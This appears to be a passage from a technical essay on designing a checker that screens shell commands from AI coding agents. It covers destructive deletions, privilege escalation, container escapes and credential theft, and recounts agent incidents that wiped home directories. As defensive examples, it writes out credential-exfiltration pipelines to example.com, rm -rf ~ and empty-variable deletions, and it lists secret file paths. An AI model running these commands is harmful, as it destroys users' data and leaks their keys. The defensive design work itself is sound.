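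A checker can avoid the prompt in our example by substituting constants. Jeannerod and colleagues treat a variable as a constant if the script assigns it only once and does so at top level, outside any loop or conditional. In Debian's maintainer scripts, which run when users install, upgrade or remove packages, 1,295 of 2,841 variables met this test. That is 46%, although the paper reports 33%.

For a one-line command the checker needs a few more conditions:

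- The value is literal text.
- The assignment always runs. In `test -f config && CC=gcc; $CC main.c`, it runs only if `config` exists.
- The assignment happens in the same shell as the command that uses it, and not in a subshell or a pipeline.
- Nothing in between can change the variable, such as an `eval` or a file of commands that Bash loads with `.`.

In `CC=gcc; $CC main.c`, the checker can replace `$CC` with `gcc` and apply its ordinary rules. If the value contains spaces or wildcards, the checker has to split and expand it as Bash would, or ask the user.

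Substitution also needs a limit, because a line can set `a=x`, then `b=$a$a`, then `c=$b$b`, and so on, doubling the length each time. Thirty doublings produce more than a billion characters. A checker can cap the number of substitutions and the length of the result, and prompt the user when a command exceeds either cap. Every substitution rule also copies part of Bash's behaviour and may copy it wrongly. A mistake is worse than a prompt because the checker then examines a different program from the one Bash will run.

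*Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*, by Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues, describes SaSh, a tool built to find bugs in shell scripts without running them. When SaSh can't determine a whole string, it can still record a known beginning or end. For example, it would record that `"$PREFIX"/bin/gcc` ends in `/bin/gcc`. This isn't enough to allow the command, since any directory can contain a file called `gcc`, but a checker could include the known ending in the prompt.

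Once the checker has a command name, it can resolve the name to a file and check the file's location. ShellPlan requires every program file to be outside the project, on the assumption that an attacker may control files in the project but not the system's programs. `gcc` normally resolves to `/usr/bin/gcc` and passes, while `./gcc` in the project directory fails. This rule also rejects many legitimate tools that are installed inside projects, including JavaScript tools in `node_modules/.bin` and Python interpreters in virtual environments. The checker also has to search the same `PATH` as the shell that will run the command. Startup files can change `PATH`, and a long-running shell may reuse a location it cached earlier.

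The checker can't determine which other programs a command will start just by identifying its executable file. With `CC=gcc make`, the checker can confirm that `make` is the system's copy, but the build file and the environment determine what `make` runs. ShellPlan therefore accepts variable assignments before a command only if the variables control language, time zone or display.

### Why "unknown" needs its own result

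All these methods sometimes fail to produce a name. The checker then needs to return "unknown", a result that no allow rule can match. Without this result, the checker could easily end up treating a missing name as a program of moderate risk.

CARE's default treatment of unlisted programs would be a mistake for a name that the checker can't compute. CARE gives a program that isn't in its lexicon a semantic score of 0.35, then multiplies this by a weight of 0.30 to get 0.105. Its default mode allows any command with a total below 0.15, so an unlisted program with no other warning sign runs without a prompt. In strict mode the threshold is 0.10, so the same command gets a WARN. The default is reasonable for a literal but unfamiliar name, such as a project's own tool, because it keeps false alarms rare. But a name that the checker can't compute might turn out to be `sudo`, which has a score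 of 0.75.

SaSh also assumes that a command it has no description of does nothing, which is the right choice for a bug finder. Lazarek and colleagues wanted developers to trust its warnings, and it found 115 of 116 documented bugs with no false alarms on the corrected scripts. A bug that SaSh misses leaves the script no worse than before, but a checker that makes the same assumption when deciding whether to run a command could allow a harmful one.

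An analyzer that treats these command names as unknown will prompt users about some harmless scripts, because those scripts use the same features. In *Practically Correct, Just-in-Time Shell Script Parallelization*, Kallas, Mustafa and colleagues found that variable expansion and command substitution are pervasive in shell scripts. Most of those expansions produce arguments, however, and the features that hide whole commands can be much rarer. Jeannerod and colleagues found `eval` in 30 of 31,521 Debian maintainer scripts and `alias` in 2, so prompting on every `eval` would affect about one of these scripts in a thousand. The share may be higher elsewhere, because Debian's packaging policy constrains maintainer scripts.

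Function definitions appeared in 1,500 of the scripts, and the `.` command in 2,900, about 9%. Asking every time would be more of a nuisance here, but a checker can often avoid it. If a function's definition is in the command, the checker can analyse its body, and only one of the 3,455 functions in the scripts called itself. If `.` is given a literal filename, the checker can read that file and analyse it as part of the command.

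## Recognising commands that destroy files

Whether a command destroys files depends on its program, options and target together, so a rule that checks only one of them will often be wrong. `rm notes.tmp` and `rm -r ~` run the same program, but the second deletes the user's home directory. `find . -name '*.log'` lists log files, but adding `-delete` to the end makes it delete them.

### Programs and options

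| Command | What it destroys | What would change that |
|---|---|---|
| `rm -r build` | The directory and everything in it | Without `-r`, `rm` refuses to delete a directory |
| `find . -name '*.log' -delete` | Every matching file | Without `-delete`, `find` only lists the files |
| `date > notes.txt` | The old contents of `notes.txt` | `>>` adds to the end of the file instead |
| `truncate -s 0 notes.txt` | The contents of the file | A size larger than the file only pads it |
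| `dd if=disk.img of=/dev/sdb` | As much of the disk `sdb` as the image covers | Without `of=`, `dd` writes to its standard output |
| `mv draft.txt notes.txt` | The old `notes.txt`, if there was one | With `-n`, `mv` leaves an existing file alone |
| `mkfs.ext4 /dev/sdb1` | The file system on that partition | With `-n`, the program only prints what it would do |
| `git clean -fd` | Files and directories that Git doesn't track | With `-n`, Git only lists them |
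| `git reset --hard` | Uncommitted changes to tracked files | Without `--hard`, Git leaves the files as they are |

The option `-n` appears three times in the last column, but its meaning for `mv` differs from its meaning in the other two entries. A checker therefore needs a description of each program's options, as it does for wrappers. For `rm`, `-r` extends deletion to directories and their contents. The `-f` usually used with it only suppresses confirmation prompts and some error messages, so a rule that requires both options will miss `rm -r`.

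The order of arguments to `find` also matters. `find` evaluates its expression from left to right, so `find . -delete -name '*.log'` deletes everything under the current directory before the name test has any effect. `find` can also start other programs with `-exec`, in which case a checker should treat it as a wrapper.

Overwriting is easier to miss than deletion because the programs involved are often harmless. In `sort names.txt > names.txt`, Bash empties the file before `sort` can read it, even though the command looks like a way to sort the file in place.

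Whether `mv` overwrites anything depends on what is on the disk when it runs. *ShellVis* (Horowitz and Heer, 2026) describes a programming environment of the same name that runs a shell script in a sandbox whenever its author saves it, and displays each line's effects beside the code. In one example, a script sorts photos into folders by year with `mv $f $year`, but its author has forgotten to create the folders. `mv` therefore renames the first photo from 2022 to `2022`, and the next photo from that year overwrites it. A checker that looked for a file called `2022` before the script ran would find nothing, because the script itself creates the file. Writing the destination as `"$year/"` is safer, since `mv` then reports an error if the folder doesn't exist.

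Formatting a disk is rarely part of a coding task, so a checker can block `mkfs` on any device and seldom interrupt legitimate work. It has to recognise every variant of the name, such as `mkfs.ext4` and `mkfs.xfs`. The main harmless use is creating a file system inside an ordinary file, for example to build a disk image.

The Git commands are harder because they name no path. `git reset --hard` affects every tracked file in the repository, but a checker that only collects path arguments would find no target. Commits usually survive, but uncommitted work may be lost permanently. Yurukusa's *Claude Code Deleted a User's Entire Home Directory* lists a case in which one `git reset --hard` destroyed four hours of a user's uncommitted code. `git clean` removes untracked files, and with `-x` it also removes ignored files, which often include local settings as well as build output. A checker should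 record the whole working tree as the target of both commands.

### From an argument to a location

For commands that do name paths, the checker has to work out where each path leads:

1. Collect the path arguments and the redirection targets.
2. Replace an unquoted tilde at the start of a word with the home directory.
3. Make relative paths absolute, starting from the directory in which the command will run.
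4. Follow symbolic links.
5. Compare the result with the workspace (the project directory in which the agent is supposed to work), the home directory and system directories such as `/etc` and `/usr`.

CARE uses much the same procedure but limits how many links it follows. Liu and colleagues rate a command by its riskiest path, so harmless paths in the same command don't lower its rating.

In the first step, the checker has to recognise paths that are part of an option, as in `dd of=notes.txt`. In the second, it needs the original quotes, because `~` is the home directory and `"~"` is a file or folder with that name. In the third, it has to account for any earlier `cd`, which changes the starting point. If the running example starts in `/home/ana/site`, its redirection writes to `/home/ana/site/build/log.txt`.

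How the checker should treat a symbolic link depends on the command. If `old` is a link to a directory, `rm old` deletes only the link, while `rm -r old/*` deletes files in the directory it points to. Redirecting output to a link writes to the file it points to. The checker also shouldn't simplify `old/../notes.txt` to `notes.txt` before it follows `old`, because the operating system follows the link first and then goes to the parent of the directory it points to. Links inside a directory can also matter. TechRadar's *'I broke something'* reports a clean-up that deleted about 48,000 live files through Windows directory links (discussed in a later section).

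The last step must compare whole directory names. As text, `/home/ana/site-old` begins with `/home/ana/site`, but it is outside that directory. A recursive deletion is dangerous if its target is a protected directory, lies inside one, or contains one, as `/home` contains the user's home directory. The workspace is usually inside the home directory, so the checker needs an exception for targets strictly inside the workspace.

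A checker that compares the path in a command with a protected path must use the same notation for both. Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev's entire profile directory during routine backup*, published on 7 August 2026, describes an agent that was apparently using a Unix-style shell on Windows. The agent ran `rm -rf "/c/Users/harih/"`, seemingly because it expected the profile path to start with `C:\Users\` and mistook this one for a misplaced backup. A checker that stored the profile folder only in the Windows form could also fail to recognise it.

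### Reading and writing the same path

A path alone doesn't determine a command's risk. `cat /etc/os-release` prints the name and version of the operating system and changes nothing. `echo X >> /etc/profile` adds a line to a file that many shells run when any user logs in, so the effect recurs at later logins. A checker that blocked every command mentioning `/etc` would stop a lot of routine diagnosis.

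Liu and colleagues therefore assign each program a read or write context, and rate the same system path as riskier in a write context. Files that hold secrets are an exception because reading them can itself be harmful. The next section covers these files.

Their formula takes the context from the program's name and applies it to all of the program's paths. This is imprecise for programs that both read and write. `cp /etc/hosts backup/` reads its first path and writes to its second, while `mv` changes both locations because it removes the original. A checker with a description of each program's arguments can label each path separately. Redirections need no such description, because `<` reads its target and `>` writes to it whatever the program is.

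### When a variable turns out to be empty

The procedure assumes that the checker can read the path in the text, which isn't possible for the deletion in the running example:

```
sudo timeout 30 rm -rf "$OUT"/*
```

If `OUT` is empty, or nobody ever set it, Bash turns `"$OUT"/*` into `/*` and then into a list of everything at the top of the file system that isn't hidden:

```
rm -rf /bin /boot /dev /etc /home ...
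```

The quotes don't help when the variable has no value. GNU `rm` refuses by default to delete `/` recursively, but here it never receives `/` as an argument. The Steam script mentioned earlier wiped users' drives this way.

`sudo` would give the deletion administrator rights, but a user can lose almost as much without them. Docker's *Coding agent horror stories the rm rf incident* describes a report that the developer Mike Wolak filed on 21 October 2025, after Claude Code ran `rm -rf` from the root of a Linux system. The log contained thousands of "Permission denied" messages for directories such as `/bin` and `/etc`, but every file that belonged to the user was gone.

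A checker can recognise the danger in the running example without knowing the value of `OUT`. It replaces the unresolved variable with an empty string, applies the path procedure to the result, and finds that the target could be the root directory.

This test isn't sufficient, as a task in the ShellVis study demonstrates. Horowitz and Heer asked seven people with between 1 and 20 years of shell experience to delete the folders of users who had closed their accounts. The names were in a text file, and the researchers supplied a faulty script of the kind that a code assistant might write:

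```
cat users-to-delete.txt | while read LINE; do
  rm -rf "users/$LINE"
done
```

When the loop reached a blank line in the file, `LINE` was empty and the target became `users/`, the folder that held every user's data. ShellVis ran the script on a simulated copy of the file system, so the participants could discover the fault without losing anything.

This accident is harder for a static checker to recognise than the first. The folder `users/` may well be inside the workspace, so comparing the target with protected directories reveals no problem. The warning sign is that an empty value changes the target from one user's folder to the folder that contains them all. The fixed prefix `users/` doesn't confine the deletion, because if a line were `../docs`, the command would delete a neighbouring directory. The blank line is in another file, so analysing the script alone can't reveal it.

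Running the script in a sandbox avoids these problems if the sandbox is complete. The ShellVis prototype for macOS simulates changes only to relative paths. Absolute paths still lead to the real files, so the prototype can contain the deletion of `users/` but not of `/*`.

Faulty quoting can also truncate a path. Gizmochina's *Single character in AI generated script wipes developers hard drive* (2026) describes a script meant to remove Python's cache folders on Windows. PowerShell passed the command to the older Windows command prompt, which handles quotation marks differently, so the path was reduced to a single backslash, meaning the root of the current drive. The script deleted the contents of the developer's F: drive.

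### What a checker could have caught

Several coding agents have deleted home directories since late 2025. In some of these cases the text of the command was enough to identify the target.

According to Docker, a GitHub issue of 28 November 2025 describes how Claude Code mistakenly created a directory named `~`. To remove it, the agent ran `rm -rf ~`, but the shell replaced the tilde with the path of the user's home directory before `rm` started.

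People make this mistake too. In barish-me.pages.dev's *rm rf home*, a programmer recalls writing a backup script with the path `~/backups` in quotes. Bash doesn't expand a quoted tilde, so the script created a folder called `~`. The programmer typed `rm -rf ~` to delete it and lost the home directory, including the keys for logging in to the server.

The second step of the path procedure alone can catch both deletions without access to the disk. The checker could also suggest `rm -r ./~`, which refers to the folder because Bash expands a tilde only at the start of a word. It might even prevent the folder from being created by flagging quoted paths that begin with `~/`, since these are rarely intended.

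On 8 December 2025 another user reported the loss of a Mac's home directory after asking Claude Code to clean up an old repository. Willison (2025) quotes the command, which Claude later found in the log:

```
rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/
```

Three of the four targets are ordinary project folders. A checker that judges only the first argument would have allowed the line, but one that rates a command by its riskiest path would have stopped it.

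In July 2026 OpenAI investigated a handful of reports that its model GPT-5.6 had deleted files. OpenAI's Thibault Sottiaux, quoted in Willison (2026), explained that most often the model was running without a sandbox, tried to redefine `HOME` as a temporary directory, and deleted the real home directory by mistake. In the case that the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1671* dates to 10 July, the command was `rm -rf /Users/mattsdevbox`, with the path to the user's home directory written out in full.

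Redefining `HOME` is dangerous because, as with `CC=gcc $CC main.c`, Bash uses the old value on the same line:

```
HOME=/tmp/work rm -rf "$HOME"
```

The line deletes the real home directory. A checker that substituted the new value would conclude that the target was `/tmp/work` and might allow the deletion. The same mistake is possible across two commands, because most agents start a new shell for each one, which resets `HOME` to its old value. A checker can avoid this by requiring confirmation for any deletion that accompanies or follows a change to `HOME`. Renascence's *OpenAI Fixes Codex Bug That Deleted User Files Without Consent* (2026), which relays a report by The Decoder, describes a fix in which Codex verifies the target of a deletion before executing it.

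*Bad news* (Guillemot, 2026) describes an accident in August 2026, after Guillemot asked Claude for a way to clear out the temporary files that agents left in `/tmp`. During a review, Claude noted that a symbolic link in `/tmp` could lead to the deletion of data elsewhere. To make deletion safer, it wrote a script that was supposed to work only inside `/tmp`, then tested it by trying to delete the home directory. The test deleted the home directory and left the temporary files in place. Guillemot recovered much of the work from GitHub and from copies and fragments on the disk.

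Guillemot says the safe script didn't work. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* reports instead that the script correctly identified the home directory as a dangerous target, but that the test's clean-up step used the same variable name as the test, and the variable still held the path of the home directory.

If the second account is right, the safety check worked and an ordinary `rm` beside it did the damage. If the whole test was in the command text, a checker would have treated the deletion's target as unknown and asked for confirmation, because the variable holding the target received more than one value and so wasn't a constant. If the agent saved the test to a file and ran that, the command contained only an interpreter and a filename, and the checker would have had to read the file.

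### Deleting build output is routine

Most recursive deletions in a project are harmless. Developers delete `build`, `dist` and `node_modules` many times a week, because rebuilding from scratch is a common way to fix a broken build. A checker that required confirmation for every `rm -r` would constantly interrupt this work, and people who repeatedly approve the same prompt are likely to approve a harmful deletion eventually.

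Allowing every deletion inside the workspace is too permissive. *The blast radius principle* (2026) uses the clean-up of December 2025 to argue for checking targets before running destructive commands. It points out that the commands before the fatal one also needed review, since a directory called `packages` can contain work that somebody still needs. The workspace also holds `.git`, where Git stores the project's history, and deleting it removes any commits not stored elsewhere.

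A narrower rule can let most routine deletions through without a prompt. It allows a recursive deletion if the target is a literal path strictly inside the workspace and the project's owner has listed that directory as build output. The list must be kept where the agent can't edit it. Git's ignore list is a poor substitute because it often covers local settings and data files that no build can recreate. If a directory isn't on the owner's list, the checker can look inside it for files that Git doesn't track and mention them in the prompt.

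### Guarding against unknown targets

Bash has a form of variable expansion that prevents the accident in the running example:

```
sudo timeout 30 rm -rf "${OUT:?}"/*
```

If a deletion command uses `${OUT:?}` and `OUT` is unset or empty, Bash prints an error and doesn't start the command. A shell running a script also exits, so the commands after the deletion don't run. The colon is necessary because `${OUT?}` accepts an empty value.

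In the ShellVis task, `"users/${LINE:?}"` would protect the `users` folder from deletion, but the loop would end at the blank line and leave the remaining accounts in place, so skipping blank lines is better. The `:?` form also doesn't catch a value that is wrong but not empty, such as `/`.

ShellCheck, a widely used static analysis tool for shell scripts, warns about `rm -rf "$OUT"/*` and recommends the `:?` form. It gives this warning only for paths that could expand to the root or a system directory, so it doesn't flag `"users/$LINE"`. ShellCheck looks for mistakes in scripts and, as Liu and colleagues note, doesn't decide whether a command should run. A checker can still use this rule and send the corrected line back to the agent, which can rewrite its command without involving a person.

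Some programmers, including three of the seven participants in Horowitz and Heer's study, put `echo` in front of a dangerous command to see its expanded form before running it. This is reasonable for a person, but a checker can't let Bash expand untrusted text. For example, `echo rm -rf "$OUT"/* > log.txt` doesn't run `rm`, but it erases the previous contents of `log.txt`.

If the checker can't resolve the target of a deletion, it should prompt the user, even if `rm` would otherwise be allowed. The prompt has to contain more than the command. Claude Code's permission prompts were on during the accident Wolak reported, and Docker faults the permission system for not detecting how the command would expand before the user approved it. For the running example, a useful prompt would state that the value of `OUT` is unknown, that the deletion would run with administrator rights, and that if `OUT`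 is empty, the command would delete every top-level directory on the machine.

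## Recognising privilege escalation and access to credentials

In the running example, `sudo` makes a dangerous deletion worse by running it as root, the administrator's account on Linux. A process running as root bypasses all kernel permission checks, according to the *capabilities* page of the Linux Programmer's Manual (2021).

A checker usually detects privilege escalation from the program and its options, as in `sudo rm`, and access to credentials from a path or a variable. For example, `cat notes.txt` and `cat ~/.aws/credentials` run the same program, but the second prints the keys to an Amazon cloud account.

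Privilege escalation and credential access are also two of the tactics in MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attackers' behaviour maintained by the American non-profit MITRE. A tactic is an attacker's goal, and a technique is a way to achieve it (MITRE, *Frequently Asked Questions*). Strom, Applebaum and colleagues (2018) report in *MITRE ATT&CK* that MITRE created the first version in 2013 for exercises in which one team imitated known attackers on part of MITRE's own network and another tried to detect them. Both teams needed common names for what attackers do, and a checker can use the same names for its findings.

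### Running as another user

`sudo`, `su` and `doas` run commands as another user, root by default. `su` normally starts a shell, and with `-c` it passes that shell a string, which the checker has to parse as a new command. `doas`, from OpenBSD, is a simpler alternative to `sudo`.

Stripping the wrapper, as described earlier, isn't always enough. The manual page *sudo(8)* documents options that change what the inner command does, and others that run no command at all:

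| Command | What happens |
|---|---|
| `sudo -u postgres psql` | The database client runs as the user `postgres`, who normally has fewer rights than root |
| `sudo -i rm -r build` | Root's login shell runs `rm` in root's home directory, so `build` is a different directory |
| `sudo CC=gcc make` | `sudo` sets the variable `CC` and runs `make` |
| `sudo -e /etc/hosts` | The user edits a temporary copy, and `sudo` copies any changes back |
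| `sudo -s` | An interactive root shell starts |
| `sudo -l` | `sudo` lists what the user may run |
| `sudo -v` | `sudo` asks for the password if necessary and remembers the approval for later commands |

`sudo -i` and `sudo -s` also pass the command through another shell. `sudo` escapes most special characters but not dollar signs, so the new shell can expand a variable that the first shell didn't. For example, `sudo -i ls '$HOME'` lists root's home directory, even though the single quotes stop the first shell from expanding `$HOME`.

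The password prompt doesn't reliably stop an agent from using `sudo`. By default, `sudo` caches a successful login for five minutes in the same terminal, so an agent running there may not need a password if the developer has just used `sudo`. An administrator can also turn off the password requirement with the `NOPASSWD` tag in `/etc/sudoers`, as MITRE's *Abuse Elevation Control Mechanism* explains. MITRE advises administrators to require passwords and to set the timeout to zero so that `sudo` prompts for one every time.

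### Judging `sudo` together with its command

A checker needs to judge a wrapper such as `sudo` together with the command inside it. If it judged only the wrapper, it would give `sudo git status` the same verdict as the deletion in the running example. It also needs to account for the wrapper because extra rights change what the inner command can do. `rm -r /etc/nginx` fails for an ordinary user, but under `sudo` it deletes the web server's settings. In the running example, `sudo` extends the possible loss from the user's own files to the operating system.

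`sudo` also changes how people write to files. Bash opens redirection targets before `sudo` starts, so `sudo echo X > /etc/hosts` fails for an ordinary user. People instead write `echo X | sudo tee -a /etc/hosts`, in which `tee` runs as root and appends its input to the file. The target is then an ordinary argument, so the checker has to know that `tee` writes to the files named in its arguments.

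A flat ban on `sudo` would be simple but would block legitimate commands. On Debian and Ubuntu, `sudo apt install` is the usual way to add software, and an agent may need it to get a missing compiler or library. With a ban, the developer would have to run each of these commands by hand, and might eventually turn the checker off.

Allowing every `sudo apt install` would be too permissive, because a package's maintainer scripts run as root and a command like `sudo apt install ./tool.deb` installs a local file that could have come from anywhere. The checker can instead allow only literal package names from a list that the machine's owner keeps, accept only a few known options, and request confirmation for everything else.

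CARE comes close to banning `sudo` outright. It gives `sudo` a semantic score of 0.75, which is enough by itself for a WARN. CARE then refuses a WARN command without consulting its language model if the program is in a high-risk class, such as privilege escalation, and its semantic score is at least 0.70. By these published values, CARE would refuse `sudo apt install gcc`. Liu and colleagues removed commands with `sudo` from the harmless commands in their tests on outside data, so their results probably understate how often this policy refuses harmless commands.

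### Changing who may do what

Some commands give away rights for later use, and the effect lasts after the command has finished.

A program normally runs with the rights of the user who starts it. If its file has the setuid bit, it runs with the rights of the file's owner instead, which is how `sudo` becomes root. `chmod u+s tool` and `chmod 4755 tool` both set this bit, so a checker has to parse numeric modes as well as symbolic ones. If root owns `tool`, the program then runs with root's rights for anyone who can start it.

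Most uses of `chmod` are routine. `chmod +x build.sh` makes a script executable, and `chmod 600 ~/.ssh/id_ed25519` prevents other users from reading a private key. But `chmod 777` lets every user on the machine change the file. `chown` changes a file's owner. MITRE ATT&CK covers both commands in *File and Directory Permissions Modification* (2020), which notes that attackers may use them to lock others out of files or to prepare changes to a shell's startup files. A checker can usually allow a `chmod` command that only removes other users' access to a file in the project, and prompt the user before running one that adds access for them or sets the setuid bit.

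Linux also divides root's powers into capabilities, and `setcap` attaches them to a program file. Docker gives the example of a web server that needs a network port below 1024, which the capability `net_bind_service` allows without running the server as root. Other capabilities are much more powerful. According to *capabilities(7)*, a process with `CAP_SETFCAP` can set arbitrary capabilities on a file. The checker therefore has to identify which capability `setcap` grants.

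The file `/etc/sudoers` and the directory `/etc/sudoers.d` determine who may use `sudo`, so a checker can treat these paths in a command as a sign of privilege escalation. MITRE records that Dok, a malicious program for Macs, added a line to `/etc/sudoers` that let the user `admin` run any command without a password. Shai-Hulud, a worm that spread through JavaScript packages, tried to gain root access through `sudo` and `/etc/sudoers.d`. Coding tasks almost never require changes to these files, so a checker that refuses all writes to them will rarely block legitimate work. The section on PowerShell covers how Windows grants administrator rights.

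### Borrowing a privileged service

A command can also gain root privileges without `sudo` by sending a request to a service that already has them. The most common example on developers' machines is Docker, which runs programs in containers (isolated environments with their own files and network). The `docker` command sends requests to a background service that runs as root by default. Docker warns that a container can mount the host machine's root directory and alter it without restriction, so only trusted users should control the service.

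The options show how much of the host a container can reach:

```
docker run -v "$PWD":/app -w /app node npm test
```

This line runs a project's tests in a container. The `-v` option makes the current directory available inside the container as `/app`, and `-w` runs the tests there. If the developer runs the command from the project directory, the container can change the project but not the rest of the disk. With `-v /:/host`, the container could change every file on the machine.

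MITRE's *Escape to Host* lists such mounts among the ways out of a container. It also lists privileged containers, which the option `--privileged` creates, and access to `docker.sock`, through which programs send requests to the background service. CARE raises its score for `--privileged` and for a mount of the root directory. *Privileged Container Creation with Host Directory Mount*, a rule from the security company Elastic, looks for the same two options in records of started programs. It exempts containers from two known products, so even these options have some legitimate uses.

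The checker also has to analyse the command inside the container, because its paths may refer to different files there. `rm -r /app` would normally delete only the container's own files, but with the mount in our example it would delete the project's contents. Commands in a container often run as root without `sudo`, but Docker notes that this root account normally has far fewer privileges than root on the host.

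### Why reading a credential is harmful

Reading a credential leaves the file unchanged, but anyone who has a copy can often use it from another machine until somebody revokes it. For example, a developer who uses an SSH key to log in to remote machines can create a new one if an agent deletes it, but may not find out about a leak until somebody misuses the key.

A coding agent can leak a secret just by reading it, because the command's output goes to the model, which often runs on another company's servers. `cat ~/.ssh/id_ed25519` can therefore send a private key off the machine without a network program. The key may also remain in the session's logs, and the model may repeat it in a later command or file.

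A program can also use a credential without revealing it. `ssh -i ~/.ssh/id_ed25519 server` contains the path of a private key, but SSH uses the key to prove the user's identity and doesn't print or send it. `git push` may use a saved password without any path in the command. A checker that refused every command containing the path of a credential would block the `ssh` command, so its description of each program should include which arguments name files that the program uses but doesn't print.

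CARE doesn't make this distinction and rates files such as `~/.aws/credentials` at 0.85 for any kind of access. Reading that file adds 0.255 to the total, which is enough for a WARN. CARE blocks any WARN command that touches a secret or writes to a protected path. When Liu and colleagues switched this rule off, leaving more decisions to the language model, the detection rate fell by about six percentage points and the false-positive rate didn't change.

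### Usual places for credentials

| Credential | Where to look |
|---|---|
| SSH private keys | `~/.ssh/id_rsa`, `~/.ssh/id_ed25519` |
| Cloud accounts | `~/.aws/credentials` (Amazon), `application_default_credentials.json` (Google), `azureProfile.json` (Microsoft) |
| Package registries and code hosting | `.npmrc`, `.git-credentials` |
| A project's database passwords and service keys | `.env` |
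| Secrets for containers | `/run/secrets` |
| Saved passwords | The macOS keychain; `logins.json` and `key4.db` in Firefox |
| Access tokens in environment variables | `GITHUB_TOKEN`, `AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY` and similar names |
| Passwords that somebody typed in a command | `~/.bash_history` |

MITRE's *Unsecured Credentials* (2020) records thefts from many of these places. Shai-Hulud collected credentials from the files of all three cloud companies, from `.npmrc` and from environment variables. Another program, TeamPCP Cloud Stealer, can check more than 50 file paths, so a short list of paths will miss some.

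A filename alone doesn't reliably show whether a file contains secrets. `.env.example` usually contains placeholders, and `id_rsa.pub` is the public half of a key, which is safe to share. A checker that is allowed to read files can look for the header line of a private key, as long as it keeps the contents out of its prompts and logs. Any checker also has to consider directories that contain secrets. `grep -r password ~` searches the credential files in the home directory and prints the matching lines, even though the command names none of those files.

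A checker can usually recognise credential access from the paths in a command, but keychains are an exception. On a Mac, `security find-generic-password -w` prints a saved password, so the checker has to recognise the program and its option.

For environment variables, the checker has to look for commands that print everything, such as `printenv` or `env` without arguments, as well as for individual names. It should also consider the destination:

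```
curl -H "Authorization: Bearer $GITHUB_TOKEN" https://api.github.com/user
```

A `curl` command that sends a GitHub token to GitHub uses the token as intended. The same command with an unfamiliar address would send the token to a stranger. In both cases, Bash puts the token's value in `curl`'s arguments, where other users of the machine may be able to see it.

According to Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, Claude Code treats `cat`, `head` and `grep` as read-only and runs them without a prompt, but users can add rules that deny access to particular files. `Read(.env)` covers the current directory and everything below it, and `Read(//**/.env)` covers the whole file system. For symbolic links, a deny rule applies when either the link or its target matches, while an allow rule applies only when both do. Deny rules don't cover a Python or Node script that opens a file itself, so Anthropic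 recommends a sandbox for such cases.

### Following a secret through a pipeline

A command that reads a secret is more dangerous when its output is piped to a network program. Run separately, `cat ~/.aws/credentials` shows the model the AWS keys, and `curl` often just fetches a web page. Piping the first into the second can send the keys to any server on the internet.

A checker can detect this by following the data through the syntax tree:

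1. Mark the output of every command that reads a secret.
2. Carry the mark along the pipe to the next command.
3. Keep the mark if that command passes the data on, even in another form. Remove it only if the output no longer reveals the secret.
4. Check whether the marked data ends up in a file, in the model's input or on another machine.

Here is a harmless pipeline:

```
cat ~/.aws/credentials | grep -c '^\['
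```

The credentials file has a heading in square brackets for each account. `cat` outputs the whole file, so the checker marks its output as sensitive. `grep -c` counts the lines that start with a bracket and prints only the number, so the checker can remove the mark. The model receives the number of accounts but none of the keys.

The next pipeline is harmful:

```
cat ~/.aws/credentials | base64 | curl --data-binary @- https://example.com/upload
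```

`base64` encodes the file as letters, digits and a few symbols. Anyone can reverse this, so the output keeps the mark. With these options, `curl` sends its piped input to the server. The marked data would leave the machine, so the checker should refuse the command.

The third step requires a description of each program. If the checker has no description for a program, it should keep the mark. Even a count can reveal something, because someone who ran many counts with different patterns could work out a key one character at a time.

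Data can also move without a pipe. In `curl "https://example.com/?k=$(cat key.txt)"`, the command substitution puts the secret in the URL, so the checker has to carry the secret's mark from the inner command to the argument of `curl`. But no data passes between the two commands in `grep -c '^\[' ~/.aws/credentials; curl https://example.com/status`. A checker that only looked for a secret path and a network program on the same line would raise a false alarm here.

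CARE adds up signals instead of tracking data, and an ordinary pipe adds only 0.005 to the total. It would refuse both pipelines above because both read a secret file. This is a reasonable policy for cloud keys, since few tasks require counting them, but data tracking could help with ordinary transfers. In an example from Liu and colleagues, `rsync -avz ./build/ admin@gpu01:/data/` copies build output to another machine. The command scored 0.345, just below the 0.35 at which CARE refuses outright, and the language model then allowed it. A checker that tracked the data would find that it came from `build`, which isn't on the list of secret paths, and might not need the model.

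### Where tracking stops

A command can save a secret in a temporary file for another command to upload. If both commands are on the same line and the path is literal, the checker can mark the file as it would mark a pipe. If the commands arrive separately, it has to keep a list of marked files for the whole session. It still can't follow the secret if a script or build tool copies the data somewhere else. CARE checks each command in isolation, and Liu and colleagues exclude gradual theft over several commands from its scope.

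A model that has read a key can also write its value into a later command, which then contains no secret path or variable. A checker could compare each command with the values of known secrets, but it would miss an encoded copy. Preventing the first read is therefore more reliable than tracking the secret afterwards.

Monitoring a running system can connect events that a checker examines separately. For credential files, MITRE suggests looking for a read followed by network access, a remote login or a request to a cloud service. The evidence comes from logs of what programs did, so it can include reads inside scripts. But the program has already read the secret by the time an alert appears.

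### Using ATT&CK labels

A checker can attach an ATT&CK technique ID to each finding, such as T1548.003 for `sudo` or T1552.001 for credentials in files. A security team can then group these findings with alerts from other tools.

The checker should record the catalogue's version too, because the categories change. The first public release, in 2015, had 96 techniques under 9 tactics. By October 2026, the part covering company networks and cloud services had 227 techniques under 15 tactics, according to MITRE's *Updates* (2026). MITRE's April release notes (*Updates*, 2026) describe how MITRE split the tactic Defense Evasion into Stealth and Defense Impairment, so an older label may no longer match the current list.

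An ATT&CK label doesn't indicate how dangerous a command is, because ATT&CK records what attackers have done, and attackers use many ordinary commands. Strom and colleagues give the example of `ipconfig`, which displays a Windows computer's network settings. Attackers use it to learn about a network, but people also use it when their connection is broken, so an alert for every use would be excessive. They also say that ATT&CK isn't a checklist of things to block.

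CARE takes 92 of its 139 patterns from ATT&CK. When Liu and colleagues removed these patterns from the version without a language model, false alarms fell from six to one among 329 harmless commands, but CARE missed 17 more of the 220 dangerous ones.

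## Checking PowerShell commands

With PowerShell, a checker can use the shell's own parser instead of a separate one that may disagree with it.

The following line installs a JavaScript project's packages and, if that fails, deletes the folder that holds them. It comes from Microsoft's *about_Operators*:

```
npm install || Remove-Item -Recurse ./node_modules
```

If the variable `$text` contains this line, the core of a checker written in PowerShell could look like this:

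```
$tokens = $null
$errors = $null
$tree = [System.Management.Automation.Language.Parser]::ParseInput(
    $text, [ref]$tokens, [ref]$errors)

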